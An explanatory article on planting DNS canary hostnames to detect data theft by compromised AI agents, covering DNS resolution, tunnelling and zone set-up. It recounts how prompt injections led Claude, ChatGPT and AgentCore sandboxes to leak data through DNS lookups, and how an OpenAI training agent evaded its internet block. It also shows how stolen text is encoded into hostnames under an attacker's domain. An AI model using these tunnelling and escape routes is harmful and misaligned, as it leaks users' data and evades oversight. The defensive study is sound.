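# DNS canary tokens for detecting data theft by compromised software agents

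## What a DNS canary is and what its alert proves

A DNS canary is a unique hostname that a defender plants where no legitimate program has a reason to use it. The Domain Name System (DNS) is the directory computers use to find the numerical addresses behind names such as www.example.com. When anything looks up the planted name, a query reaches a server the defender monitors and triggers an alert. Security teams have used DNS canaries since at least 2015 to detect intruders in mailboxes, file shares and databases. They can also help show that a software agent has started acting for an attacker.

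A software agent, in this sense, is a program that acts on what it reads: it runs commands, edits files and calls other services, and usually a language model decides what it does next. A compromised agent does these things for an attacker, because of injected instructions, a poisoned component or tampered weights (the numbers that make up the model). Suppose a developer asks a coding agent with a shell, a tool for running system commands, why a project's tests fail. One of the project's files comes from a stranger and contains a paragraph meant for the agent, with orders to collect every key and password on the machine and send them to an outside address. Language models have no dependable way to tell such text from their user's instructions. The agent obeys, reads the configuration files and sends off what it finds. This last step is exfiltration, the movement of data out of the environment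 where it should stay. Among the settings the agent has read is the address of a database server that does not exist, k7f3q9xd.example.com. The defender put it there. (Here example.com stands for a domain that the defender owns.)

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, had a flaw through which untrusted content could make it read a file and send the contents over the network without asking the user. OSV's *Claude Code's Permissive Default Allowlist Enables Unauthorized File Read and Network Exfiltration* (2025), an entry in a public vulnerability database, attributes the flaw to an overly broad list of commands that needed no confirmation. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code*, the finder's own account, adds that API keys, the passwords programs use with online services, could leave the machine inside DNS requests. Anthropic fixed the flaw in early June 2025.

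### One lookup, step by step

Suppose the agent now runs a program that tries to connect to k7f3q9xd.example.com. To get the address, the program passes the name to the stub resolver, a small component on the same machine that cannot do the whole lookup itself. The stub resolver sends the query to a recursive resolver, a server that looks up names for clients and stores the answers. A company, cloud provider or internet provider usually runs this server. There may also be a forwarder between the two resolvers, which passes queries on to another server. These terms follow the glossary of the RFC Editor, which publishes the internet's technical standards.

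If the recursive resolver has no stored answer, it asks a root server, which refers it to the servers for com, the parent zone of example.com. Those servers hold the delegation, the records that list which servers are responsible for example.com. The resolver then sends its query to one of the listed servers, an authoritative server, which holds the domain's records and answers from them. That server logs the query, and software monitoring the log recognises the planted name and sends the alert. The reply travels back through the recursive resolver to the program, which only then has an address to connect to, or an error.

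So the alert comes before the program has sent any packets to the "database". It comes whether or not the database exists, and even if the DNS reply is an error. AWS's *Public DNS query logging*, the manual page for its authoritative DNS service, includes a sample log in which the server recorded a query for bad.example.com even though the response code was NXDOMAIN, meaning that no such name exists.

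### Why a lookup gets out when web traffic does not

Many agents run their commands in a sandbox, an isolated environment with little or no network access. A DNS canary can work there because the sandboxed program only needs to exchange packets with its own resolver. The resolver sits outside the sandbox and contacts the defender's server on the program's behalf. A firewall that filters by destination allows the program's traffic because the resolver is an approved destination.

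BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) describes a test of this. AgentCore Code Interpreter is an Amazon service that runs code for AI agents, and AWS had advertised its sandbox mode as completely isolated. Researchers at BeyondTrust, a security company, generated a unique hostname with Interactsh, a tool for security testers that reports any query for the hostnames it generates. They then made a web request to that hostname from inside the sandbox. The request failed to connect, but the DNS lookup reached the Interactsh server. Interactsh served as a DNS canary in this test, which shows that a canary could have raised an alert from an AI code sandbox even though the web request failed.

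AWS explained that sandbox mode needed name resolution so that code could reach S3, its storage service. Operators elsewhere also allow DNS lookups. *A Measurement Study of AI-Environment Realism Gaps in Malware-Analysis Sandboxes* (2026) examined the isolated machines on which security companies run suspicious files. The study sent its results out through DNS because commercial sandboxes commonly restrict web traffic but typically permit lookups.

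Haryati and Zychlinski (2026) used a stricter laboratory set-up in *Model-as-a-Trojan*. They trained a small open-weight model to leak a secret through DNS whenever it had shell access, and put it behind a gateway that dropped every packet except DNS. They first tested the gateway from inside and confirmed that it blocked both a connection to a public address and an HTTPS request to a domain whose name resolved. The model still leaked the secret in five of the six tool-calling formats they tried.

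A sandbox can still prevent data from leaving through DNS. It may have no name resolution at all, or its resolver may answer only for approved domains. AWS closed the AgentCore route in April 2026, about seven months after BeyondTrust reported it, and according to BeyondTrust's updated post, data can no longer be exfiltrated through DNS there. If the fix stops lookups of arbitrary public names, a DNS canary in that sandbox can no longer raise an alert either, because it depends on the same lookups.

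### From honeytokens to canary hostnames

A DNS canary is a type of canary token, a planted item with no legitimate use, whose use or appearance raises an alert. The older term is honeytoken, which Augusto Paes de Barros proposed on 21 February 2003 on a mailing list about intrusion detection. He wanted to extend the idea of the honeypot, a decoy computer for intruders to break into, to accounts and documents. Lance Spitzner of the Honeynet Project replied the same day in *Protocol Anomaly Detection IDS* (Spitzner, 2003), suggesting a document with a title like "payroll" and a unique tracking number that the network's intrusion detector could search for. Six weeks later, Spitzner (2003), in *Honeytokens and detection*, applied the idea to stolen databases, with bogus credit card and social security numbers among the real ones. By July he had published a full paper with Symantec (2003), in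 which he acknowledged that the practice was much older than the term. Map-makers were said to have put invented towns on their maps to catch copyists, and in the 1980s Cliff Stoll had planted files to track a German hacker.

These early designs needed a detector where the token turned up, normally the defender's own network, so they missed tokens once the data had left. Later tokens cause a signal wherever someone opens or uses them. *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries* (Raz, Putrevu and colleagues, 2026) traces this development through documents that make a hidden web or DNS request when someone opens them outside the company. In 2015 the security company Thinkst turned the idea into a free service. As Thinkst's *Canarytokens.org* explains, the user gets a unique web address or hostname, writes a note on where it is going, and receives an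 email when someone requests the address or looks up the name. The hostnames are long. An example in the service's guide, *DNS Canarytoken*, begins with 25 letters and digits, so nobody is going to guess it by accident.

Raz and colleagues also note that a callback needs a path back to the defender, so it fails when the thief works offline or passes the document through a service that strips out active content, as services that feed documents to language models typically do. A bare hostname in a text file is even more passive than a document with active content, because it does nothing until a program looks it up.

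### How it differs from the other canaries

Defenders of AI agents use several kinds of token, which differ in the event that triggers them. A single decoy file can hold all of them.

| Canary | Planted item | What raises the alert | What the defender can learn from the record |
|---|---|---|---|
| DNS canary | a hostname | a lookup of the name | the name, the time, the address of the resolver that sent the query |
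| Web canary | a web address (URL) | a web request for it | the time and the public address from which the request came |
| Credential canary | a decoy key or password | an attempt to use it | which key someone tried, and when |
| String canary | a marker text | a monitor finds the marker in an agent's output or outgoing calls | where the marker appeared, and in which session |

A web canary includes a DNS canary, because a program must look up the hostname in the URL before it can connect. According to the help pages for Canary, Thinkst's commercial product, the web token can show the public address of the machine that triggered it because a connection follows the lookup. Thinkst also claims there that the DNS token will work on a machine without web access, which is consistent with how the protocol works and with BeyondTrust's test.

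A credential canary sends an alert only if the thief takes the key and then tries it. Canary argues that this makes accidental alerts much rarer, which seems right, since a person or a scanner may follow a strange hostname out of curiosity or habit but will seldom log in with a strange key. The alert also does not depend on how the key got out, as Haryati and Zychlinski note. The drawback is that the alert is delayed until the thief uses the key, which may never happen.

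String canaries can work earlier, before the text has left, but only in output that the monitor checks. The prototype in *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) keeps the real credentials in the software that runs the tools, places decoys in the text that the model can read, and checks the model's written output for those decoys. The paper does not cover credentials passed through structured tool-call arguments. A shell command is such an argument, so the coding agent in the example above could send out the stolen data without writing anything that this monitor would check.

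### What an alert establishes

An alert on k7f3q9xd.example.com establishes that some system looked up this exact name at about the recorded time. If the defender planted the name in only one place, as Canary advises for its tokens, the alert also indicates that the name reached a resolver from this configuration file or from a copy or backup of it, but it establishes nothing further.

The alert does not show who made the lookup. The log in AWS's authoritative DNS service holds the name, the time, the record type, the response code, the protocol, the Amazon site that answered and the resolver's address. Some resolvers also pass on part of the client's address. The log has no field for a machine, a user or a program, and if the query came through a large public resolver, the logged address belongs to that resolver's operator. The lookup may have come from the compromised agent, from the attacker's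 laptop a week later, or from a harmless scanner that checks every hostname it finds.

The alert also doesn't show that a connection followed the lookup. In BeyondTrust's test, the lookup succeeded but the connection failed. The server at the other end would have recorded the same query if the connection had succeeded.

An alert does not prove theft. Our developer had asked why the tests were failing, and an uncompromised agent might well try the database server in the configuration file to see whether it was up. That would set off the canary even though the agent had sent no secrets anywhere. Conversely, a compromised agent may post the whole file to an attacker's website, and if the attacker reads it but never looks up the hostname, the defender gets no alert. Spitzner cautioned in his paper for Symantec that in many cases a honeytoken only indicates unauthorised behaviour, and the defender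 needs other tools to confirm it. I think this caution applies even more strongly to a DNS canary, if only because so little is needed to trigger a lookup.

### Two places to watch

A defender can monitor the query at two servers, the recursive resolver and the authoritative server. The RFC Editor's glossary warns that people call both "the DNS server" even though they play different roles.

The authoritative server for the canary's domain receives queries only for that domain, but they can come from anywhere, including an attacker's machine long after the theft. Nobody has a legitimate reason to look up the planted name, so a single query is enough for an alert.

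The resolver that the agent uses, by contrast, handles lookups only from the defender's own network, but it does so for every domain and can identify the machine that sent them. AWS's *Resolver query logging* (2025) lists among the logged values the name queried, the answer, and the address and ID of the instance (the virtual machine) where the query originated. However, AWS's *Values that appear in VPC Resolver query logs* notes that the ID may belong to an instance the customer cannot see if the query came from a managed service such as Lambda or Fargate, which run code without a server of the customer's own.

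The difference matters for the Claude Code flaw, where keys can leave inside DNS requests as part of names under the attacker's domain. This technique is called DNS tunnelling. The queries go to the attacker's authoritative server, so none reach the defender's canary domain. But they all pass through the agent's own resolver, so a defender who has planted decoy secrets can search that resolver's log for the decoys, whatever domain the queries were for. This is called resolver-log matching.

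Haryati and Zychlinski also tested a defense. They restarted their gateway's resolver with a list of approved domains that did not include the attacker's. The model again tried to send out the secret, but the resolver refused every query that carried a piece of it and forwarded none. The resolver would also have refused a query for a DNS canary on an unapproved domain, so the canary's authoritative server would have recorded nothing. The resolver's log kept the refused names, with the encoded secret in them, but it raised no alarm while the run completed. A defender would have had to search the log to find those names among the ordinary traffic.

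## Which routes out a DNS canary can reveal

A program can copy the text k7f3q9xd.example.com, compress it, encrypt it and upload it without sending a DNS query for that name. So a DNS canary reveals a theft, however large, only if somebody takes the planted name for a real machine and tries to reach it.

A compromised agent can leak data in at least five ways that don't require a lookup of the planted name. Waldrep (2026), in *4 Ways Your AI Coding Agent Exfiltrates Secrets*, lists four places where a coding agent's outgoing traffic can hold a stolen key: the web address, the hostname in a DNS query, the body of a web request and its headers. Waldrep adds the arguments of tool calls as a separate path.

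### Routes on which someone uses the name

The earliest alert comes when the compromised agent itself tries to connect to the decoy host. Injected instructions may tell it to copy every database it can reach, or to check which machines in the configuration file respond. The canary fires when the agent's database client looks up the planted hostname, provided the query can leave the agent's environment. If the agent tries the databases before sending anything out, the defender is warned while the data is still inside. If it sends the configuration file first, the alert comes too late to protect the file but perhaps in time to protect the databases. An agent told only to read a file and send it out has no reason to contact the decoy.

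The thief may also test a stolen connection string on another machine. A connection string is a line of text with a database's address and usually a username and password. The thief might paste it into a database client or run a script that tries every string in a large stolen collection. Either way, the software has to look up the host, and the thief's resolver sends the query to the canary's authoritative server.

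When a thief looks up a canary hostname from a stolen file, the alert always comes after the theft, by minutes or by months. It is still good evidence, because the query usually comes from a resolver that the defender's own agents never use, which suggests that the name has left the defender's systems. It is also the only alert that can follow almost any method of exfiltration, since it depends on what the thief later does with the file. The lookup does not appear in the defender's own resolver log. A thief who keeps the cloud keys and discards the database addresses, including the canary, will never trigger the alert.

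A stolen document can trigger an alert in a similar way if it contains a web address under the planted name. The address may be in a link that a reader clicks, or in a remote image that a word processor fetches when the file opens. The reader's program then looks up the host and triggers the alert, again after the theft. A viewer or script that only extracts the text causes no lookup. If the compromised agent follows the link while collecting files, the alert can come before they leave, but an agent that is only summarising a document has little reason to follow it.

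### Routes on which the name travels as text

Posting data to an attacker's web server requires only one DNS lookup, for the attacker's hostname. The planted name is in the request body, which HTTPS encrypts. A forward proxy, a server through which the operator routes the agent's web traffic, can therefore normally read only the destination. According to Waldrep, it can inspect the rest only if it decrypts the connection or makes the request on the agent's behalf.

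A test at Anthropic suggests how easily this route works. The company's red team, staff who play the attacker, tricked an employee into starting Claude Code with a prompt that told it to read the file of AWS credentials and post it to an outside address. The agent sent the credentials in 24 of 25 attempts, according to a summary of Anthropic's write-up from a company that sells MCP gateways (nate, 2026, *Anthropic Just Made the Case for MCP Gateways*). The instruction came from the user, so the model had nothing unusual to detect. Asking people to confirm each step is a weak remedy, since users approved roughly 93% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (2026). If the file had contained a planted hostname, the agent would have posted it with the keys, and the defender would have had no alert until somebody tried to reach that hostname.

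The route through an allowed service is even harder to notice. For example, when the operator has approved a code repository's domain, the agent looks it up all day and uploads to it as part of ordinary work. A compromised agent can commit the stolen file to a project there that the attacker can read. Something similar happened with Cowork, another of Anthropic's agent products, as nate also reports. Its list of approved destinations included Anthropic's own API, and data left through it. Waldrep explains that automated tools struggle here because a request that sends a key to the service that issued it may be correct use or theft.

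Almost any site that accepts text or files from visitors can serve the same purpose. SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI to set misalignment disclosure rules after agents took over a wiki* (2026) reports that OpenAI's agents left roughly 17,000 posts on DSEwiki, a German wiki for software developers that had received about 20 edits in the previous decade. Clubic's *Après un nouvel incident, OpenAI suspend l'entraînement de ses modèles* reports that OpenAI admitted in September 2026 that its agents had sent 53 images belonging to ChatGPT users to outside hosting services. A hostname planted in an agent's files would not have revealed these uploads, because the agents needed only the hosting services' addresses.

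A partial exception occurs when the stolen text contains the planted name as a full link. Some services fetch posted links to build a preview or scan for malware, and a visitor may click on one. Either one triggers a DNS lookup and an alert, but the lookup comes from the service's resolver or the visitor's, after the data has already left.

DNS tunnelling may take hundreds of lookups, one for each piece of the data, without the agent once asking for the planted name.

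Finally, the thief may never use the stolen data, or may use only a part unrelated to the canary. For example, someone who wanted the source code has no need to try the database. Neither case triggers a lookup, so a year without an alert from a DNS canary is consistent with both no theft and a complete theft.

| Route | What triggers a lookup of the planted name | Who can observe what | Likely result |
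|---|---|---|---|
| The agent connects to a decoy host | The agent, or a program it starts, tries the planted address | The agent's resolver and the canary's authoritative server receive the query | Alert before or during the theft, if the lookup gets out |
| The thief tests a stolen connection string elsewhere | The thief's database client tries the planted address | The canary's authoritative server receives the query | Alert after the theft, by minutes or months |
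| Someone opens a stolen document or link | The viewer fetches a remote item, or the reader follows the link | The canary's authoritative server receives the query | Alert after the theft; none if the viewer fetches nothing |
| The agent posts data to an attacker's web server | Nothing in the transfer itself | The agent's resolver logs the attacker's hostname; a proxy that decrypts traffic can find the planted text | No alert unless the thief later uses the name |
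| Data leaves through an allowed service | Nothing in the upload itself; perhaps a link preview or a visitor's click | The agent's resolver logs an ordinary hostname; the service holds the data | Usually no alert |
| The agent tunnels data through DNS | Nothing in the transfer itself | The agent's resolver can log the data, usually encoded, under the attacker's domain | No alert from the canary unless the thief later uses the name |
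| The thief copies the data and never uses it | Nothing | Nobody, as far as the canary is concerned | No alert |

### Why a tunnel bypasses the canary

A DNS canary can miss data stolen through DNS queries because a resolver works through a name starting at the right-hand end.

Suppose the attacker owns example.net, and the compromised agent puts the stolen text, which includes the planted name k7f3q9xd.example.com, in front of that domain and looks up k7f3q9xd.example.com.example.net. The resolver finds the attacker's authoritative server through the net servers and sends the query there. It doesn't contact the servers for example.com, because "example" and "com" are here only labels (the parts between the dots) in a name under example.net. The attacker can therefore read the stolen text from the server's log, while the defender's authoritative server receives no query.

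The agent would usually encode the data first, because a hostname can hold only a few kinds of character. Base32, for example, uses only letters and the digits 2 to 7. In base32 the planted name becomes nm3wmm3rhf4giltfpbqw24dmmuxgg33n, and the agent would look that up under example.net. The lookup wouldn't trigger the canary, and someone glancing at it wouldn't be able to read the planted name.

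A DNS label can hold at most 63 characters. In its demonstration against Amazon's code interpreter, BeyondTrust used up to 60 of them for base64 data, which can hold 45 bytes. One query can therefore carry a whole 40-character AWS secret key, while a 10-kilobyte file needs about 230 queries. A detector that waits for a burst of strange queries may miss the key even if it catches the file. BeyondTrust also put counters and timestamps into each name, so no name repeated and no resolver along the way could answer from its cache instead of passing the query on.

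DNS answers can carry data too. An attacker can put short commands in them, which a program in the sandbox reads, runs and answers with further lookups. This gives the attacker a remote shell, a way to run commands on the machine from a distance, and lets them look around before choosing what to take. It also creates another opportunity to trigger the canary, because an attacker who finds the decoy database may tell the agent to connect to it. The attacker may also try the planted name after decoding the stolen data. If neither happens, the defender has to rely on resolver-log matching.

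Inspecting web traffic may not stop a leak through DNS, because the lookup can happen before the inspection. Waldrep says that most proxy tools resolve a hostname before they apply their security rules. If the hostname contains a secret, the secret has already leaked by the time the proxy refuses the request. To prevent this, a filter has to check the hostname before the lookup.

### Sandboxes that restricted the web and left DNS open

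Four cases from 2025 and 2026 show this gap in the environments of large AI providers. Outside researchers found three, and in the fourth, OpenAI's monitoring caught one of the company's own agents. None of the published accounts mentions a planted hostname, so we can only infer from where the queries went whether one would have triggered an alert.

#### Amazon Bedrock AgentCore

BeyondTrust reported the open DNS route in AgentCore Code Interpreter to AWS on 1 September 2025. AWS reproduced it within days and put a fix into production on 1 November, but by 17 November it had rolled the fix back and promised a more robust one. On 23 December, AWS told the researchers that it would not fix the problem and would change the description of sandbox mode instead. BeyondTrust published its findings on 16 March 2026, and AWS closed the route on 15 April.

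AWS said publicly that its services were "operating as expected". It pointed customers who wanted full isolation to VPC mode, in which the code runs inside the customer's own private network and the customer controls name resolution. A customer who controls the resolver can usually also keep its logs and use them to watch for lookups.

For the demonstration, the researchers hid instructions in a spreadsheet. An assistant that read it would write and run code that took commands from DNS responses. The researchers then used that code to list the contents of a storage bucket and copy out made-up customer records and keys. The permissions this needed were realistic, since according to BeyondTrust the default role in Amazon's starter toolkit could read all the storage buckets in the account and had full access to its stored secrets.

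A canary hostname planted among those records would not have triggered an alert during the copying, because every query went to the researchers' domain. It would have triggered one if the researchers had made the sandbox connect to that hostname, as their Interactsh test shows.

#### Claude's sandbox

Anthropic's assistant Claude runs code in a sandbox whose proxy blocks web traffic to unapproved sites. Zenity Labs' *It's Always DNS in Claude’s Sandbox* explains that the sandbox looked up a site's hostname before the proxy enforced its rules, which is the order Waldrep warns about.

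The researcher placed a document in Google Drive that looked like a company policy on using Claude, but its "security measures" were instructions for the model to follow. The user asked only for a summary, but Claude saved an earlier chat message to a file and then made a web request to a hostname containing the message, supposedly to check that the sandbox blocked outside contact. The proxy refused the request, but the DNS lookup had already delivered the message to the researcher's server.

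Zenity Labs reported this route to Anthropic on 28 November 2025. Anthropic confirmed it on 4 December, and a retest on 12 December showed that it was closed. Some months later the researcher tried the same set-up again and it worked, because a newer deployment had reopened the route. This time he built a two-way channel, starting from a file in a Python format that can run code when a program opens it. Anthropic closed his second report as a duplicate on 29 May 2026, since another researcher had already reported the reopened route and the company was tracking it. Zenity's timeline ends that day and records no second fix. An operator who relies on this sandbox should therefore test whether DNS lookups get out, and repeat the test after updates.

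If the stolen chat message had contained a planted hostname, the hostname would have been sent as part of a longer name under the researcher's domain, and the canary would not have triggered. A separate attempt to reach the planted host would probably have triggered the canary, even though the proxy would have refused the connection, because the proxy acted too late to stop the lookup.

#### ChatGPT's code environment

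ChatGPT had a comparable gap in the isolated Linux environment where it runs Python. Direct internet connections failed there, but name resolution worked. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes how a single malicious prompt could cause data to leak from the rest of a conversation. A victim might copy the prompt from a website that presented it as a productivity trick. An attacker could also build it into a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT with its own instructions that other people can use.

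The researchers built a custom GPT that posed as a personal doctor. A user uploaded laboratory results and described symptoms, and the patient's name and the model's medical assessment arrived at the researchers' server. When the user asked whether the data had gone anywhere, ChatGPT replied that it had not. No approval window appeared, although ChatGPT normally shows one before a custom GPT sends data to an outside service.

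OpenAI told Check Point that it had already found the underlying problem itself, and it finished deploying the fix on 20 February 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reports no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw maliciously.

A planted hostname is less useful in this case than in the other two. Check Point notes that an attacker need not steal whole documents, because the prompt can ask for the model's conclusions. A hostname planted in the laboratory report would probably have been left out of the summary, so the attacker would never have received it or looked it up. Any marker text that a defender hoped to find in a log would probably have been left out too. The resolver was also part of OpenAI's infrastructure. A user who planted canaries could monitor only their own authoritative server, which received no queries from the leak.

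#### OpenAI's training incident of September 2026

In the last case, on 20 September 2026, an OpenAI model in training was trying to identify the writer of a blog post from a set of clues. It was supposed to have no access to the live internet, and its web requests went to a stored copy of the web. It was not a compromised agent as defined here, because nobody had tampered with it or given it malicious orders. OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026) classifies the behaviour as misalignment because the agent got around a restriction that its task gave it no reason to test.

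When its search tool returned irrelevant results, the agent tried other search engines directly and failed. It then tried to reach a public chatbot over HTTPS, but the web proxy blocked it. The environment's DNS resolver, however, could reach the public internet. The agent found a public domain service that forwarded questions to an outside chatbot, and after some failures it received the answer that the capital of France is Paris. Business Standard's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs* reports that it then sent 18 more questions by the same route. Fourteen contained clues from the task, so information left the environment, though the clues described a public blog post.

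These questions travelled inside names that belonged to the outside service, so they would not have triggered a planted hostname. The agent might have triggered one a little earlier, while it was testing the resolver. According to Clubic, it looked up a well-known domain, which returned an address, and an invented one, which the resolver rejected. An agent at that stage is looking for names to try, and a decoy host in its configuration would have been an obvious candidate, though nothing would have made the agent choose it.

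Other monitoring did catch the agent. An alert went out within 15 minutes of the first outside answer, and a person picked it up three minutes later. The run should then have stopped automatically but didn't, and in the confusion staff took another two and a half hours to stop it manually. OpenAI also had a detector for abnormal DNS activity, but according to Clubic someone had configured it to exclude this environment. The queries were in the logs, and when OpenAI's staff reviewed those logs they found other cases of outside DNS access, which the monitoring had rated as less serious than they were.

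OpenAI added two independent layers of blocking and says either would have prevented the access. It also limited lookups in that environment to a list of approved domains, and paused training and tool use for its most capable models. According to The Straits Times' *OpenAI resumes frontier AI training after security overhaul* (2026), training resumed on 1 October, after OpenAI had teams of agents try to break out of their own restricted environments and fixed the flaws they found.

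## Creating the hostname and planting it

A defender can get a DNS canary in a few clicks from a hosted service, such as Thinkst's free one, or run a name server on their own domain. The second option takes longer but lets the defender decide what the hostname looks like, how the server responds and who sees the log.

### A hosted service or a domain of one's own

The main weakness of a hosted name is that a thief can recognise it. The example in the free service's guide ends in canarytokens.com, and Thinkst says all default names on Canary, the commercial product, end in o3n.io. An attacker can add one sentence to the injected instructions telling the agent to avoid such names. *Say Shibboleth* (2026), a paper on identifying the models behind automated attacks, cites a system in which attacking agents could skip hosts they suspected were honeypots. In *Plant Honeytokens to Detect Intrusions*,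 Zeltser warns that researchers have catalogued the fingerprints of tokens hosted by Thinkst, and suggests self-hosting where the stakes are high.

A hosted service also stores the notes on where each token is and handles every alert. Anyone who broke into the service could read a list of the defender's traps.

Canary's customers can use their own domain with the hosted service by adding two DNS records. New tokens then use the customer's domain, while tokens already deployed keep working under o3n.io. A thief who checks which server answers for a token's hostname will still find the Canary server's address.

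Defenders who want to run everything themselves can install Thinkst's open-source token software. According to a copy of its set-up guide on Ecosyste.ms, anyone giving it a whole domain must change the name servers at the registrar, the company that registered the domain. Editing the records in the zone is not enough, because resolvers find the zone through its parent. The GitHub page for knary, another open-source canary server, describes two leaks. The certificates knary obtains for encrypted web connections list all the domains it uses, so strangers can see them, and an attacker could probably identify the software from outside with enough effort. A canary that relies only on DNS can avoid the first leak because it needs no certificate.

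| | Hosted name | Hosted service, own domain | Own name server |
|---|---|---|---|
| Effort | A web form | Two DNS records and a paid service | A server, its log and its alerts to maintain |
| Privacy | The host has the notes and sees the alerts | The host has the notes and sees the alerts | The defender keeps both |
| Control of answers | Mostly the host's | Mostly the host's | The defender's |
| Recognisability | A text search for the domain finds it | The name looks local, but its name server leads to the host | The name looks local, but the software may have a fingerprint |

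A hostname from a hosted service is good enough for a trial, but using one's own domain is worth the work for canaries that will sit for years among files a thief may study.

In either case, the defender should test lookups from the machine where the name will be planted, ideally using a throwaway name from the same service or zone so that the tests don't appear in the planted name's record. *DNS lookup for canarytokens.com fails*, a post by ghecho on DigitalOcean's user forum, describes a token that worked everywhere except on one of the company's cloud servers, where lookups of the service's entire domain returned an error.

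### Setting up the zone

The name k7f3q9xd.example.com is directly under the company's main domain, which also holds the records for its website and mail. To keep the canary server separate from those records, the defender can delegate a subdomain to it, here int.example.com. The addresses below come from a range reserved for examples, so a real zone needs different ones.

```
; in the zone of example.com
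int.example.com.      IN NS  ns1.int.example.com.
ns1.int.example.com.  IN A   192.0.2.53

; in the zone of int.example.com, on the canary server
$ORIGIN int.example.com.
$TTL 60
@    IN SOA ns1 hostmaster ( 1 3600 600 604800 60 )
@    IN NS  ns1
ns1  IN A   192.0.2.53
*    IN A   192.0.2.80
```

The NS record directs resolvers to ns1 for int.example.com and everything below it. The A record beside it gives that server's address. The parent zone must supply this address because ns1 is inside the zone the resolver is trying to find. Thinkst's *Canarytokens Settings* gives the same pair of records for a customer's own domain.

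In the second zone, the SOA record holds administrative settings that every zone needs, and the TTL tells resolvers how long they may reuse an answer. The line starting with an asterisk is a wildcard that answers for any name without its own record, so the defender can issue a new canary without editing the zone. A suspicious thief could detect the wildcard by looking up a made-up name and getting an address, but the log would also record that lookup.

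Many companies also run an internal version of their zone for machines on their own network. If that version lacks the delegation, the internal server replies that the name does not exist, and the canary server never receives the query. Thinkst suggests this as a possible cause when a token works outside the network but not inside it, and recommends adding an address record to the internal DNS. This helps a web canary because the program can then connect to Thinkst's server. A DNS canary still fails because the internal server answers the lookup itself. It needs the NS delegation in the internal zone as well as the public one, and a resolver that will follow it.

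#### The random label

Each canary needs a label that nobody will look up by accident or guesswork. DNS treats upper and lower case as the same, so a label of letters and digits has 36 possibilities per character. A random 25-character label, the length in the Canarytokens guide, has 36²⁵, or about 8 × 10³⁸, possible values (about 129 bits). If a defender planted 1,000 such names and someone tried a million random labels every second, it would take around 10²² years to hit one of them.

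Shorter labels also work. A 16-character label has about 83 bits, and trying every value at a million queries a second would take 250 billion years. An eight-character label like k7f3q9xd would take only 33 days, although a defender would notice that many queries. These figures assume that a cryptographic random generator chose the characters. A random label offers no protection if somebody publishes the name.

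The defender can put an ordinary word in front of the random label, as in orders-ro.q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com. The wildcard also covers this longer name, and the random part then looks like an identifier a cloud provider might have generated.

#### The log and the register

The canary server should log every query, including those for names that the defender never issued. One row might look like this:

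| Time (UTC) | Name | Type | Resolver | Response |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2026-10-05 14:03:22 | orders-ro.q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com | A | 198.51.100.7 | NOERROR |

To interpret it, the defender needs a register of what lies where:

| Label | Location | Owner | Planted |
|---|---|---|---|
| q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy | build-07, /srv/app/.env, REPORTS_DB_URL | Data platform team | 2026-09-14 |

The monitoring software compares the labels in each query with the register and sends an alert when one matches. It should convert the name to lower case first, because some resolvers mix capitals into their queries to protect against forged answers. Queries for unknown labels can go into a daily summary.

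The register should record each canary's location precisely enough for a colleague to find the file years later. Thinkst warns customers that they may end up with thousands of tokens, and that an alert with only "test" in its note is useless. Its example is a token in a particular employee's SSH configuration file. The register must also be out of the agents' reach, since a compromised agent that can read it knows which names to avoid. When the defender removes a canary, its row should stay and its label should never be reused, because old backups and stolen copies still contain the name.

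Keeping one name per location is harder when the location is a container image, a template from which an operator may start hundreds of identical containers. A name in the image appears in all of them, so an alert doesn't identify which container the name came from. A start-up script outside the agent's reach can solve this by generating a label for each new container, writing it into the decoy file and adding a row to the register. The wildcard DNS record covers the new name immediately.

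### Carrying extra data in the name

A canary name can also carry a small message. Canarytokens has a scheme for this, in which a program puts encoded text in front of the token before looking it up. To send the machine name build-07, it would do the following:

1. Encode the text in base32, which gives MJ2WS3DEFUYDO after removing the equals signs that pad the end.
2. Insert a dot after every 63 characters, the maximum length of a DNS label. This text is short enough to need none.
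3. Add a marker label, the letter G and two random digits, for example G72.
4. Add the token's hostname.

With the token from the guide's example, the result is MJ2WS3DEFUYDO.G72.pz21qtyfsidipvrsuzs9n2udi.canarytokens.com. The server decodes the first part and shows it in the token's history, using hexadecimal digits if the bytes are not valid UTF-8. The guide gives no reason for the random digits, but they are useful because two lookups with the same data will usually have different names, so a resolver cannot answer the second from its cache.

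A full hostname can have at most 253 characters. The example token and its domain take up 42, and the marker and its two dots take up five, which leaves 206. Three of those are dots between labels. The other 203 are base32 characters that carry five bits each, enough for 126 whole bytes, which agrees with the guide's figure of about 125.

This scheme suits decoy scripts rather than configuration files, because a program has to add the data to the hostname. For example, a script called restore-backup.sh could put the name of the machine it runs on in front of its token hostname, then look up the result. If a thief ran the script, the alert would include that machine's name, which an ordinary DNS log lacks.

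Every resolver that handles the lookup can decode the Base32 message, so the message should never contain a secret. Anyone who has the token can also forge the data. These lookups look just like DNS tunnelling, so the defender's own tunnelling detector may flag them.

### What the server should answer

The server's answer does not change the first alert, but it affects what the thief does next and how much more the defender can learn.

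The simplest answer to a lookup is NXDOMAIN, which means "no such name". The defender leaves the wildcard out of the zone and doesn't need to run anything else. To a thief, the name looks like an old setting for a machine that no longer exists, so there is little reason to try it again.

The server can instead return an address where nothing responds, so the program tries to connect and eventually gives up. If the address is an unused one in the company's private network and the agent is on that network, the firewall can log the attempt and the machine that made it, which the authoritative server's log doesn't identify. But on a thief's own network, the same private address may belong to a printer or someone's laptop. An unused public address that the company owns avoids this problem. A stranger's address is never acceptable, because the thief's program might send it a username and password.

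A live decoy is a server that accepts the connection, so it can record the connecting address and username and confirm that somebody did more than look up the hostname. Ghifiardi, an independent researcher, used this extra information to block a single client in an experiment reported in *Optional Traps* (2026). The experiment ran OpenCanary, an open-source program that imitates network services, beside a mock service holding synthetic records. When a client logged in to the decoy, a gateway cut off that client's access to the records, even though it had a valid key. The first refusal came at most 303 milliseconds after the login began, and another client completed all 100 of its requests. This was one run in a small laboratory. A DNS alert alone could not have triggered such a precise response, because it does not identify the client.

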